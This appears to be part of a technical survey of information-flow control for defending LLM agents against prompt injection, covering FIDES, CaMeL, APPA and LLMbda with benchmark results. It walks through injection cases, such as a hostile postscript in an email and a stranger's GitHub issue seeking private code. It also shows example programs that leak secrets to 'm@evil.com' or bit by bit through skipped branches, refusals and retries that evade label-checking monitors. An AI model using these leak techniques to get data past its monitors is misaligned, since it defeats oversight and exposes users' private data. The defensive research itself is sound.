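Suppose an observer must not be able to tell two inputs apart, such as a mailbox with a meeting invitation and one without, and no visible action is correct for both. A deterministic agent that satisfies noninterference shows the observer the same actions for both inputs, so it gets at least one of them wrong.

Sampling does not remove the problem. Let P₀ and P₁ be the probability distributions of the visible actions for the two inputs, and suppose the agent succeeds with probability at least 1 − e on each. The distance between the distributions is the largest difference between the probabilities they give to any one set of outcomes. Then

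```
P₀(C₀) ≥ 1 − e
P₁(C₀) ≤ 1 − P₁(C₁) ≤ e            because C₀ and C₁ do not overlap
distance ≥ P₀(C₀) − P₁(C₀) ≥ 1 − 2e
```

Noninterference requires a distance of zero, so e must be at least one half. An agent that handles both mailboxes correctly 95% of the time has a distance of at least 0.9, and an observer can identify the mailbox 95% of the time by checking which set the actions fall into. If there are n possible inputs and no two of their correct sets overlap, a noninterfering agent succeeds on at least one input with probability at most 1/n. For example, a noninterfering agent that must book one of ten medical specialists according to a secret diagnosis will be right at most a tenth of the time for at least one diagnosis.

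A data-dependent task may not meet this condition. Suppose there are three possible mailboxes, and each rules out a different one of three days for a meeting. Any two mailboxes leave one day in common, but no day suits all three. An agent that must ignore the mailbox can guarantee at most a two-thirds chance of being right, which it gets by choosing a day at random.

These limits hold for any model, however capable, even when nobody is attacking. Completing such a task reliably requires relaxing the property, for example by having the user endorse the email or by letting the planner learn one bit from it.

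### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, mainly with GPT-4o, a 2024 OpenAI model. They attacked each agent with injected instructions that named its tools. An agent without policies carried out 152 injections. The number fell to 20 with Tool Filter, a defence in which the model first discards tools it predicts will be unnecessary, and to 21 with FIDES when its policies were switched off. When the monitor enforced the policies, no injections succeeded with any planner.

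That zero follows partly from how the researchers set up and scored the test. They labelled a data field as untrusted if some injection in AgentDojo targeted it, so the labels matched the attacks in advance. AgentDojo's own checks still recorded three successful attacks against FIDES, which the researchers rejected after inspecting the runs by hand. Across the planners, the successes they rejected included blocked calls that AgentDojo had counted as completed and actions that the policies permit. For example, the policies allow a Slack message without a link to be sent from an untrusted context if it leaks no confidential data. Noninterference for integrity would not allow an injection to cause such a message.

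The table gives the percentage of user tasks that GPT-4o completed when it was not under attack. The variable-passing planner hides untrusted results and can neither inspect them nor query a quarantined model.

| | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no policies | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Basic agent, policies on | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| Variable passing, policies on | 48.0 | 44.0 | 56.3 | 35.2 |
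| FIDES, policies on | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |
| Share of tasks that are data-dependent | 5.0 | 10.0 | 43.8 | 42.9 |

With policies on, FIDES beat the basic agent by about 8 points on average. It did worse than the basic agent in the travel environment, where the policies let the basic agent use many of the necessary tools even in an untrusted context, and GPT-4o often confused the variables that FIDES had to handle. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks and led the basic agent by 16 points overall.

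Some tasks failed because the policies worked as intended. In several banking tasks, the agent has to read a file and follow its instructions. Reading the file makes the context untrusted, so the monitor blocks the payment no matter how good the model is.

The variable-passing planner also completed some data-dependent tasks that it should not have been able to complete. Costa and colleagues attribute these successes to lenient scoring, lucky guesses, and tasks where doing nothing happened to be correct. A guess can pass a test that uses only one version of the data, even if it would be wrong for another version. In one banking task, the user wants a new password if a suspicious transaction has occurred. FIDES classified a transaction as suspicious because the amount was large, without reading the description, and changed the password. Its context was still trusted because the amount had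 a trusted label, although a stranger who sends the user money can choose the amount.

### How often a person has to approve

When a policy blocks a call, an agent can ask its user for permission instead of giving up. Kolluri and colleagues argue that this changes how one should measure the cost of a defence. Earlier evaluations counted a blocked call as a failure for the defended agent but let the undefended agent act without restriction. In practice, many products make an undefended agent ask before every consequential action. With v as the number of policy-violating calls in a run, they propose two measures:

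```
HITL load  =  the sum of v over all tasks the agent completes
TCR@k      =  the share of all tasks it completes with v ≤ k
```

HITL stands for "human in the loop" and TCR for "task completion rate", so TCR@0 is the share of tasks that need no approval. The HITL load covers only completed tasks, so an agent can lower it by failing at the tasks that need the most approvals. Comparing loads is therefore meaningful only between agents with similar completion rates.

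Kolluri and colleagues also built Prudentia, a version of FIDES whose planner receives the policies and its own context label. Before inspecting a variable, the planner must explain why and list the calls it plans to make afterwards. The table shows results on AgentDojo with o3-mini, a small reasoning model from OpenAI. The basic agent in the top row asks for approval of every consequential call.

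| Agent | HITL load | TCR@0 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Basic with labels and policies | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

With the newer o4-mini and no limit on approval requests, Prudentia completed 73.2% of tasks and needed 19.2 approvals. FIDES completed 75.7% but needed 36.8 approvals. On WASP, a benchmark of web browsing with injected instructions, Prudentia blocked every attack and never needed approval. The user tasks in WASP consist of upvoting or commenting on a post, so they are all data-independent, and the derivation above does not limit them.

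Prudentia reduces approvals partly by letting the user endorse data instead of approving each action. Kolluri and colleagues describe an email that lists ten chores. If the agent reads the email without an endorsement, its context becomes untrusted and the user must approve ten separate calls. If the user endorses the email first, its text counts as trusted and the agent can do all ten chores without asking again. This is less secure, because an eleventh instruction that an attacker hid in the email would also count as trusted. Kolluri and colleagues decided against an equivalent shortcut for secrets because they thought that whether a user should release private data depends too much on the recipient and the occasion.

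The AgentDojo figures for approvals come from runs without attacks and assume that the user would approve every call in a successful run. Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that people who face frequent prompts start approving them without much thought. They leave the design of the approval dialog, which an attacker might try to manipulate, to future work.

### Deployment

In May 2026, Microsoft (2026) announced FIDES as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, the company's toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes another version, off by default, in GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent. That version keeps a single context label and so far enforces policies for only some GitHub tools and no tools from other providers.

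The GitHub policy targets a known attack. A stranger opens an issue in a public code repository and asks for information from a private one, and an agent with access to both posts the answer publicly. Under the policy, reading the issue marks the agent's context as untrusted, and reading the private code marks it as secret. The monitor blocks public posts when the context is both untrusted and secret.

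A single label for the whole context can be too coarse for office work. In Microsoft's example, Alex's agent reads an email from Priya with early sales figures and another from Marco, who isn't allowed to see those figures. Only Alex is allowed to read both emails, so the agent cannot reply to Marco without approval, even if the reply mentions no figures.

The sample policy for Teams, Microsoft's workplace chat service, follows robust declassification. If the agent's context is trusted, the agent may send any content to any channel. If the context is untrusted, the monitor compares the channel's members with the permitted readers. A model that misunderstands a trusted request can therefore post a secret to the wrong channel without triggering a check. The policy's protection also depends on which data is labeled trusted. The GitHub integration labels everything in a private repository as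 trusted, so an injection that an employee pastes into a private issue would reach the planner as trusted text.

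## CaMeL: leaks through skipped branches and retries

FIDES runs a fixed loop and lets secrets influence which tools the agent calls. CaMeL, the Google DeepMind design that builds on Willison's pattern, has the planner write a whole program before any untrusted data arrives, and tracks what the program's branches reveal. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). They did not prove that it satisfies noninterference, and called formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work. Garby, Gordon and Sands later studied CaMeL's interpreter in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (2026) and found two leaks, one when a program skips a branch and another when the agent retries after a failure.

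### A program written before the data arrives

In CaMeL, the privileged model reads the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter made of ordinary code runs the program, calls the tools and passes untrusted text to a quarantined model.

Garby and colleagues reproduce an example from the CaMeL paper in which a user asks for a meeting reminder to be sent to whoever wrote the latest email. An attacker has added a postscript to that email, asking for a cancellation note instead. An ordinary tool-calling agent read the email and sent the cancellation. A planner in the style of CaMeL writes something like this:

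```
email   = get_last_email()
address = quarantined_model("Extract the sender's address", email)
send_email(to=address, subject="Meeting reminder", body="We have a meeting.")
```

The program fixes the subject and body before anything opens the email, so the postscript cannot change them. The postscript can still change `address`, which the quarantined model extracts from the email. CaMeL therefore gives every value a label, which its designers call a capability. The label records which sources contributed to the value and who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the labels against that tool's policy.

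Programs can also branch, so the interpreter needs a program-counter label:

```
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL refuses this call because the condition is secret, even though the message is a constant. Explicit secrecy would allow it.

Such tracking works only if every feature of the language passes labels on correctly. Garby and colleagues found that when a program inserted an untrusted value into a string, the interpreter treated the resulting string as trusted. That bug is limited to one feature, but the leak through skipped branches affects any monitor that updates labels only when assignments execute.

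### What a skipped branch reveals

CaMeL's interpreter makes a variable secret when the program assigns to it inside a branch with a secret condition. If the program skips the branch, the assignment never happens and the label stays as it was. The following program uses this twice:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
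```

The table shows the values and labels in the two possible runs.

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| Start | `tmp` is True, public; `rich` is True, public | `tmp` is True, public; `rich` is True, public |
| First `if` | assignment runs: `tmp` is False, secret | assignment skipped: `tmp` is True, public |
| Second `if` | assignment skipped: `rich` is True, public | assignment runs: `rich` is False, public |
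| Third `if` | the email goes out | no email |

At the end, `rich` is public in both runs, but its value reveals whether the balance exceeds the threshold. When the balance is high, the condition of the second `if` is secret, but the assignment to `rich` is skipped, so `rich` doesn't get the secret label. When the balance is low, `tmp` is still public after the first `if`, so the assignment to `rich` appears to depend only on public data.

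Fenton described this leak in 1974, and Denning rewrote it as a conventional program two years later. Fenton's own machine avoided it by fixing each variable's label, but CaMeL's labels change as the program runs. Buiras, Stefan and Russo warn in *On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems* (2014) that naively adding such labels to a purely run-time monitor can open a "high bandwidth covert channel".

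A stranger cannot simply ask CaMeL's planner to write such a program, because the planner does not read the stranger's text. The planner could write one by accident, however, and a single variable is enough if the observer notices when no email arrives:

```
notify = True
if account.balance <= threshold:
    notify = False
if notify:
    send_email("adviser@bank.example", "Please call me.")
```

If the balance is high, the program skips the assignment, `notify` stays public, and the interpreter allows the email. If the balance is low, the adviser gets no email. Programmers often set a default and override it in a branch, so a planner trained on ordinary code may well do the same.

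### Refusing to change public data in a secret branch

The standard repair is the *no-sensitive-upgrade check*, which stops the program when it is about to assign to a public variable while the program-counter label is secret. In the program with two variables, the run now stops at `tmp = False` if the balance is high and finishes without sending anything if the balance is low, so the observer receives no email in either case.

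The same rule has to apply to a model's conversation, which is also data a program can change. Garby and colleagues show this with a program that tells GPT-5.2 to remember that x is false. In a branch with a secret condition, the program tells the model to set x to true. After the branch, it asks the model for the value of x. Their interpreter stops the run at the message inside the branch. Marking the conversation as secret at that point would not have prevented the leak, because a run that skipped the branch would still have had a public conversation.

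The check also stops harmless programs because, as Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues note, it ends a run even if the program never uses the variable again. *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (Austin and Flanagan, 2009) lets the assignment proceed and marks the variable as "partially-leaked", which postpones the decision to stop. Another solution is to label the variable secret before the branch, so that its label is the same in both runs. The planner then has to predict which variables a secret will affect, and it can no longer use those variables to decide on public actions.

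Even with the check, the program with `notify` leaks one bit, because it sends an email if the balance is high and stops before the email if the balance is low. But the program can do nothing further once it has stopped, whereas under CaMeL's original rule it could test one bit of the balance after another in the same run and send or withhold an email for each.

### How much a run can leak by stopping

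With the check in place, a monitor can provide *termination-insensitive* noninterference. Smith's definition of it compares only the final memories of runs that finish. This suits a program that produces output only at the end, but an agent sends messages and makes other visible calls while it runs. *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, 2008) gives the example of a program that prints its secret and then loops forever, which satisfies the definition because it never finishes.

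Their own definition covers output that appears before a run ends. For a deterministic program, write out(μ) for the sequence of public outputs it produces from memory μ, and count a normal finish as a last output. The definition is then equivalent to

```
μ ≈ ν   implies   out(μ) is a prefix of out(ν), or out(ν) is a prefix of out(μ)
```

One sequence is a prefix of another if the second begins with the first or equals it. A secret may therefore cut the outputs short but may not change any of them. The program with `notify` meets this condition under the repaired monitor, because one run produces an email and a normal finish and the other produces nothing. It fails under CaMeL's original rule, because the run without an email still produces a normal finish.

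Researchers often said informally that a property of this kind leaks at most one bit. Askarov and colleagues show that this is wrong for programs with output:

```
for i in range(maximum):
    output(i)
    if i == secret:
        loop forever
```

The last number the program outputs is the secret. Three established tools for checking information flow, Jif, FlowCaml and the SPARK Examiner, accept programs of this kind because the numbers are not computed from the secret and the branch that depends on it assigns nothing. The secret also leaks if the program crashes instead of hanging, or if a monitor ends the run with a refusal.

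Askarov and colleagues also prove that no program satisfying the definition can do much better than this brute-force count. After any sequence of outputs, only one next output is possible, and the alternative is silence. The observer can therefore learn only where the outputs stopped. For an observer who sees up to t outputs, and a secret of N bits whose values are all equally likely, this gives

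```
number of distinguishable observations    ≤  t + 1
chance of guessing the secret correctly   ≤  (t + 1) / 2^N
```

In their experiment, a second process monitored a value that the program kept updating and treated the program as hung when the value stopped changing. It recovered a 32-bit secret in under six seconds. At the same rate, recovering a credit card number of about 50 bits would take about 18.5 days, and recovering a 128-bit encryption key would be infeasible.

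An agent is much slower than such a loop. If it makes at most 100 visible calls, an observer can distinguish at most 101 cases, which is less than seven bits. That is little help in guessing a long random password, but it is more than enough to identify one of ten medical specialists.

### Why retries are worse than one long run

These limits apply only if a stopped run is not retried. When a program fails in CaMeL, the planner receives an error message and writes another program. Garby and colleagues point out that this retry loop is ordinary Python outside the interpreter, where nothing tracks labels. Each retry therefore starts with clean labels, even though earlier errors influenced the new program. CaMeL's designers acknowledge the problem and censor error messages to reduce it. Censorship can hide the text of an error, but it still reveals to the planner that the attempt failed, and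 a secret may have caused the failure.

Birgisson and Sabelfeld (2011), in *Multi-run security*, studied what happens when an attacker can run the same program repeatedly with different public inputs. Their most damaging example is a single loop:

```
while secret & mask:
    pass
```

The operator `&` keeps only the bits that are 1 in both numbers. The attacker sets `mask` to 1, then 2, then 4, and so on, and each run hangs exactly when the corresponding bit of the secret is 1. Each run leaks at most one bit, and N runs reveal all N bits, while the counting program may need 2^N outputs. On a desktop computer, a program that Jif had certified leaked about one bit per second in this way. A credit card number would take less than a minute instead of 18 days.

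Birgisson and Sabelfeld measure the damage by the set of secrets that remain possible after the attacker has tried every input:

```
K(secret)  =  all values x that give the same result as the secret, for every public input
```

The smaller K is, the more the attacker knows. For the loop above, K contains only the secret. For `while secret: pass`, which takes no input from the attacker, K contains either zero alone or every value except zero, and the attacker learns nothing more by repeating the run. They forbid loop conditions that depend, directly or through an enclosing branch, on both a secret and data the attacker controls. Whether the program finishes can then depend on one or the other, but not on the combination. They prove that a program that follows this rule and the usual restrictions on public assignments leaks at most one bit over all its runs.

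This theorem does not apply to CaMeL's retries, because it assumes that the program stays the same. CaMeL's planner writes a new program for each attempt, so the mask can be a constant in the program's text. Each program obeys the rule, but together they test the secret one bit at a time. Garby and colleagues conclude that the loop can extract an entire secret this way. The answers end up in the planner's conversation, and the planner can copy them into the next program as constants with clean labels.

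As with the planner's errors in general, a leak of this size would be unlikely to arise by accident, though smaller ones could. Failures can also carry untrusted data to the planner, as they do in f-secure. A retry may also repeat actions, such as a payment the first program made before it failed.

Even without the retry loop, the system may run more than once. An assistant that answers incoming email starts a new run for every message, so a stranger can send a different message each time and see which ones get a reply.

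### Recovering from a refusal

Ending the run after a refusal restores the limit of t + 1 observations, but it makes the agent fragile. A milder option is to add the label of whatever caused the failure to the planner's context label. If a secret caused it, the agent could continue private work but make no more public calls, so someone who sees only public calls could not distinguish this run from a stopped one. Garby and colleagues instead have their agent test its programs on mock data until one works, and only then write the version that runs on real data, so the errors it learns from cannot depend on real secrets.

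APPA, a monitor that Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, designed for tool-using agents, treats a refusal as the start of a search for a permitted way to continue. They prove that reading more data can never lift a refusal that the context label caused, because reading can only make the label stricter. An agent that responds by gathering more information is therefore wasting its time. The refusal lists the routes that the policy does offer:

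- An authority, which may be a person, a fixed rule or another model, approves that exact call.
- Trusted code transforms the data, for example by removing personal details.
- The agent first completes a required step, such as recording a legal clearance.
- A temporary copy of the agent, called a child branch, reads the data so that the main conversation's label stays unchanged.

If a child branch returns something, the main conversation normally takes on its label. As in Willison's pattern, the policy may exempt answers in a narrow format. Kravchenko and colleagues acknowledge that even these answers can carry a small amount of secret information, or can be false ones that an attacker has chosen.

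The agent relies on these routes to complete many of its tasks. Kravchenko and colleagues wrote 20 office tasks to exercise APPA's mechanisms and ran each ten times with GPT-5.6 Luna, an OpenAI model. The agent completed 88% of the runs with the full system, 56.5% without child branches, and 35% without suggested remedies. No attack succeeded in any of the three versions. The differences may be smaller on tasks that were not written to exercise these mechanisms. The scoring only checks for harmful actions, such as an email to the wrong person, so it would not detect information that leaks through refusals.

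APPA's theorems do not cover that leak either. They guarantee, for example, that a call that breaks the policy runs only with an approval for that exact call, and that a hijacked model cannot forge that approval. These are conditions on single traces, and none of the theorems compares two runs with different secrets. Kravchenko and colleagues state that their guarantee is not general noninterference.

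Some of APPA's refusals reveal nothing about the contents of the file they protect. For example, one of its test tools reads a confidential file and emails it in a single call. APPA checks the file's declared label before the tool opens the file, so it refuses to email an unauthorised recipient whatever the file contains.

Other refusals can depend on a secret. APPA keeps a log of completed actions, which the main conversation shares with its child branches, and a policy can require one action before another, such as a recorded staff review before a company-wide notice. Suppose a child branch reads a confidential personnel file and records a review only if the file contains a complaint. The main agent discards the branch, so its own label stays public, and then tries to send the notice. If APPA refuses, the agent can infer that there was no complaint, but its label stays public because only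 data admitted to the conversation can change it. If APPA allows the notice, everyone who receives it can infer that there was a complaint.

Labelling the log's entries would not fix this, because when the file contains no complaint, there is no entry to label. Similarly, when CaMeL skipped the assignment, nothing marked `rich` as secret. Each kind of entry would need a label fixed in advance, like the variables in Fenton's machine.

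## LLMbda: a proved guarantee for agents that write and run code

CaMeL's rules for labels exist only as the Python code of its interpreter, which made the leaks hard to find. Garby and colleagues instead started from the rules, defining a small programming language, LLMbda, that can express both an agent and the programs its model writes. They proved that every LLMbda program satisfies a termination-insensitive form of probabilistic noninterference, and they checked the proof in Lean. The LLMbda interpreter is part of the same Lean development.

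### A language with a conversation built in

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language built from functions, in which `λx. e` is the function that takes x and returns e. It adds data such as numbers, strings and records, and gives every value a label. It also adds one piece of state, the current conversation with the model, which has its own context label. Four operations act on the conversation. In the table, pc is the program-counter label and ctx is the context label.

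| Operation | What it does | Condition | Effect on labels |
|---|---|---|---|
| `send e` | adds the value of e to the conversation as a message | pc ⊑ ctx | ctx rises to the join of itself and every label inside the value |
| `recv` | samples a reply from the model, adds it to the conversation and runs it as code | pc ⊑ ctx | the code runs with pc raised to ctx |
| `fork e` | runs e, then restores the earlier conversation | none | the result keeps its own label |
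| `clear` | empties the conversation | pc ⊑ ctx | ctx becomes pc |

The condition is the no-sensitive-upgrade check applied to the conversation. The shorthand `@e` stands for `send e` followed by `recv`. With these operations, a quarantined model takes one line:

```
quarantine = λprompt. fork (clear; @prompt)
```

The fork sets aside the planner's conversation and later restores it with its context label unchanged, and `clear` ensures that the model receives only the prompt.

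In the basic agent loop, the context label can only get stricter. An LLMbda program can lower it with `clear`, because an empty conversation contains nothing to protect, but the new label is never lower than pc. Code that a stranger has influenced runs under an untrusted pc, so any conversation it clears remains untrusted.

### Why a reply runs under the conversation's label

A reply may be plain data or a function that the agent will call. Either way, the model computed it from the entire conversation, so `recv` runs it with pc raised to the context label. Garby and colleagues prove, in a lemma called confinement, that the result of any code has a label at least as strict as the pc it runs under, and that the code can change the conversation only if the context label is at least that strict both before and after the change. Code from an untrusted conversation therefore cannot produce a trusted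 value or add a message to a trusted conversation.

The theorems assume nothing about the parser, which turns the text of a reply into a program. Suppose an attacker fully controls what the model writes and makes it write a value with the label "trusted". LLMbda joins the new label to the labels already present, so the value stays untrusted.

Tools enforce their policies by checking labels. The expression `l ? v` is true if the label of v may flow to l, and `assert l v` stops the run if it may not. An email tool, for example, can assert that the subject and body are trusted while accepting any recipient.

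The answer to such a test also needs a label. If it took the label of v, a tool that found its input untrusted would receive an untrusted answer, which would be useless for a policy decision. If it took only pc, as in earlier work by Austin and Flanagan, the answer could leak information. For example, an observer who sees only trusted, public data cannot see a value that is trusted and secret in one run and untrusted and public in another. But a test against "trusted, secret" is true in the first run and false in the second, and the observer would see that difference if the answer were labeled only with pc.

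LLMbda instead joins l, the label in the policy, to pc. In the example, this makes the answer secret, so the observer cannot see it. An observer who is allowed to see data labelled l learns nothing improper from the answer, because that observer could already see any data whose label may flow to l.

### Nontermination as missing probability

The first version of LLMbda assumed a model that always gives the same reply to the same conversation. In the later version, the model samples each reply with a probability that depends on the conversation so far. The probability of a run is the product of the probabilities of its replies, and the probability of a final state is the sum of the probabilities of all runs that end in it.

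Suppose a program twice asks a model to flip a coin that lands heads with probability 0.3, and returns the number of heads. The results 0, 1 and 2 have probabilities 0.49, 0.42 and 0.09, which add up to 1. If the program instead loops forever after two tails, the remaining probabilities add up to 0.51, and the missing 0.49 is the probability that the program does not finish. Runs that end in an error or a failed `assert` also count toward the missing probability. A list of probabilities that add up to at most 1 is called a *subdistribution*.

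An observer at label m cannot distinguish final states that differ only in data whose labels may not flow to m. Adding the probabilities within each group of indistinguishable states gives a subdistribution over what the observer can see. Ordinary probabilistic noninterference requires this subdistribution to be the same for any two inputs that the observer cannot tell apart. The probability of reaching no final state must then also be the same, which is too strict a requirement for a system that stops some runs because of a secret.

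### When two subdistributions are compatible

Suppose an agent's public answer is A or B, and the model picks each with probability 0.5 without seeing any secrets. After picking B, the agent updates some private records. If a secret bit is 1, this update hangs 40% of the time, so the agent finishes with answer A with probability 0.5 and B with probability 0.3, and hangs with probability 0.2. If the bit is 0, it finishes with A or B with probability 0.5 each.

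Garby and colleagues first tried a definition that compares only the runs that finish, but found that it was wrong. Dividing the first pair by its total of 0.8 gives (0.625, 0.375), which differs from (0.5, 0.5). The agent would therefore fail even though the secret affects only whether it finishes, which a termination-insensitive property should allow.

They settled on a condition called *compatibility*. Two subdistributions μ and ν are compatible when there is an ω such that

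```
μ(q) ≤ ω(q)  and  ν(q) ≤ ω(q)     for every outcome q
Σ ω(q) ≤ 1
```

Informally, letting more of the unfinished runs finish could make the two distributions equal. This is possible only if the larger of the two probabilities for each outcome, added up over all outcomes, comes to at most 1. The distance in the table is half the sum of the absolute differences between the two probabilities of each outcome.

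| μ | ν | Larger values | Total | Compatible | Distance | Average nontermination |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| (0.5, 0.3) | (0.5, 0.5) | (0.5, 0.5) | 1.0 | yes | 0.1 | 0.1 |
| (0.6, 0.3) | (0.3, 0.6) | (0.6, 0.6) | 1.2 | no | 0.3 | 0.1 |
| (0.5, 0) | (0, 0.5) | (0.5, 0.5) | 1.0 | yes | 0.5 | 0.5 |

In the middle row, only a tenth of the runs on each side are unfinished, too few to account for a difference of 0.3, so the secret must have changed the answer itself.

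*Termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference*, or TIPNI, requires that any two starting points that look alike to an observer lead to compatible subdistributions for that observer. If the model is deterministic, TIPNI reduces to the ordinary termination-insensitive property. If every run finishes, neither subdistribution is missing any probability, so compatible distributions must be equal.

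For programs that sometimes fail to finish, compatibility also limits how far apart the two sides can be:

```
Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)|  =  2 Σ max(μ(q), ν(q)) − Σ μ(q) − Σ ν(q)
                 ≤  (1 − Σ μ(q)) + (1 − Σ ν(q))
```

Halving both sides shows that the distance is at most the average of the two probabilities of nontermination. The top row of the table reaches this limit. The distance does not include what an observer could learn from a run failing to terminate. If the observer can tell that a run has hung, nontermination counts as another outcome, and the limit rises to the larger of the two probabilities, which is 0.2 for the top row.

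The bottom row shows how weak TIPNI becomes when runs often hang. Its program flips a coin, loops forever if the coin differs from a secret bit, and otherwise outputs the coin, so any output reveals the bit. TIPNI permits this because half of the runs never finish. A system that restarted every hung run until one finished would reveal the bit every time, so TIPNI, like the older property, does not make automatic retries safe.

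### Where the definition came from

The definition is an instance of a general method from Hunt, Sands and Stucki (2022), *Reconciling Shannon and Scott with a Lattice of Computable Information*. They observe that the definition of Askarov and colleagues only covers programs with a single output stream and would have to be reworked for other kinds of output, such as parallel streams. Their method applies to any kind of output that can be more or less complete. It allows two outputs to differ if both could be extended to the same more complete output.

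One of their examples is a program that computes a pair of items with two separate loops. In one run only the first loop finishes, and in another only the second. Neither partial result extends the other, so a rule based on prefixes would reject the program, even though both results could be extended to the same full pair. The same is true of probabilities. Neither (0.5, 0.3) nor (0.3, 0.5) is at least as large as the other in both positions, but (0.5, 0.5) is at least as large as both.

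Garby and colleagues were the first to apply the method to probabilistic programs. They then discovered the same condition, derived in other ways, in two papers from 2011. *Non-termination and secure information flow* (Smith and Alpízar, 2011) studies a small language with random assignments and shows that its programs nearly satisfy probabilistic noninterference if they rarely fail to terminate. *Termination-Insensitive Computational Indistinguishability (and Applications to Computational Soundness)* (Unruh, 2011) uses an equivalent condition for programs that return true or false, to extend cryptographic guarantees to programs that may not terminate.

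### A proof that skips what the observer cannot see

Proving TIPNI requires finding a suitable ω for every pair of inputs that look alike. Smith and Alpízar obtained theirs by deleting all computation on secrets from a program's text. They proved that this "stripping" cannot make any public outcome less likely. An agent's code cannot be stripped in advance, because the model writes some of it during the run.

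Garby and colleagues therefore strip the computation while it runs. They define a second set of rules for executing LLMbda programs. These rules follow the ordinary ones until a label appears that the observer may not see. At that point they skip the affected computation and substitute an empty record with the same label. No agent ever runs this way, since the rules exist only for the proof. With μ₀ and μ₁ for the ordinary results from two inputs that look alike, and ω₀ and ω₁ for the results with skipping, the proof has three parts:

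- **Domination.** Skipping never lowers the probability of anything the observer can see. By confinement, the skipped code could not have changed anything visible, and it might have hung or caused an error. So μ₀ ≤ ω₀ and μ₁ ≤ ω₁.
- **Blindness.** The skipping rules never use hidden data, so the results are the same for both inputs, and ω₀ = ω₁.
- **Total mass.** The probabilities in ω₀ add up to at most 1.

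The shared ω₀ meets the definition of compatibility. For the agent that answers A or B, the skipping rules omit the update to the private records, so the result is (0.5, 0.5) whatever the secret bit is.

The proof yields slightly more than TIPNI requires, because the same ω works for all secrets at once and not only for each pair. Suppose there are N equally likely secrets and the observer sees either the final result or that there is none. The best possible guess is correct with probability

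```
(1/N) × ( Σ largest probability of q under any secret  +  largest chance of no result )
    ≤  (1/N) × ( Σ ω(q) + 1 )  ≤  2/N
```

This is the same limit that Askarov and colleagues proved for deterministic programs with a single output. The attacker's chance of guessing correctly is at most twice that of a blind guess.

### Endorsement, and what it cannot undo

Some tasks need untrusted data to count as trusted. One example from Garby and colleagues is an agent that acknowledges emails and puts a category such as "general" in the subject line. A quarantined model reads the email to choose the category, so the category is untrusted, and the email tool would reject it as a subject. The program can relabel it with `endorse`. If t is the new label and v the value, the result has the label

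```
pc  ⊔  (integrity of t, secrecy of v)
```

The secrecy part comes from v, so endorsing a secret password leaves it secret. Joining pc keeps an attacker's code from using the operation to make data trusted, because everything that code endorses under an untrusted pc remains untrusted.

Endorsement lets untrusted data affect trusted results, so noninterference no longer holds for integrity. The remaining guarantee, *Insulated TIPNI*, is that TIPNI still holds for observers who see all public data, trusted or not, and from whom only secrets are hidden. It holds however the attacker words the untrusted input and whatever the program endorses. A careless endorsement may lead a plan to pay the wrong person, but it can't make a secret flow into public data.

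The theorem treats the two parts of a label symmetrically, so exchanging them gives a declassification operation that releases secrets but preserves the integrity guarantee.

A chain of endorsements is more dangerous than a single one. Suppose a program endorses a stranger's text and then adds it to the planner's conversation. The context label stays trusted, so code that the model writes under the stranger's influence runs as trusted code, and any endorsements in that code take effect. To counter this, Garby and colleagues describe a wrapper that marks each value it endorses and refuses to endorse any value that already has the mark. They don't have a theorem that states exactly what the wrapper achieves. One difficulty is that two programs can return the same value with the same label even though only one of them lets untrusted data decide whether an endorsement happens.

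### What Lean has checked, and what it assumes

The Lean development proves TIPNI and Insulated TIPNI and connects them to the interpreter. The interpreter takes a program and an *oracle*, which is a table of prepared answers with one entry for every possible conversation at every point in a run. With a fixed table, the interpreter is deterministic. The correctness theorem is that if each entry is drawn independently according to the model's probabilities, the interpreter ends in a given state with exactly the probability that the definitions assign to that state.

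In a live run, the interpreter fills in entries as it needs them by calling the model over the internet. The theorem assumes that each reply follows a fixed distribution that depends only on the conversation and whose probabilities add up to 1. Under this assumption, the replies can be of any quality, but the service cannot remember earlier conversations. If it did, `clear` would no longer isolate the model from what it had read before.

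*PerMIT* (2026) proves integrity theorems for agents with persistent memory, checked in Lean, and warns that such a check does not show that a deployed system matches the model in the proof. LLMbda narrows this gap because its theorem is about the same interpreter that runs the agents. The proof does not cover the code that contacts the language model, the Lean compiler, or the software that connects an agent to a real service.

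### The Randori agent on banking tasks

To test whether the language is practical, Garby and colleagues used it to write an agent called Randori, named after a form of sparring in Japanese martial arts. Randori practises on mock data before it accesses the real bank account. During practice, payments do nothing and every file contains the same placeholder text. The planner then writes a final version of its program, which runs once on the real account.

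This avoids CaMeL's leaky retries but makes the agent more fragile. The agent has never run the final program. Practice does not check labels, so a plan can succeed there and then break a policy on the real account, where the agent cannot try again. The models had also never seen LLMbda, so the prompt had to teach them its syntax.

The tests used the banking environment of AgentDojo, with 16 user tasks and nine attacks on each. The models were OpenAI's GPT-5.2, Alibaba's Qwen3.7-plus and Xiaomi's MiMo-v2.5. Each model ran every pairing of task and attack three times, which gives 1,296 attacked runs. Garby and colleagues also ran CaMeL on two of the models, with and without its policies. The table shows the share of user tasks completed.

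| Agent | Model | No attack | Under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | 65.0% |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 63.4% |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 59.5% |
| Randori without endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 62.5% | 60.2% |
| Randori without endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 54.2% | 56.2% |
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 71.1% |
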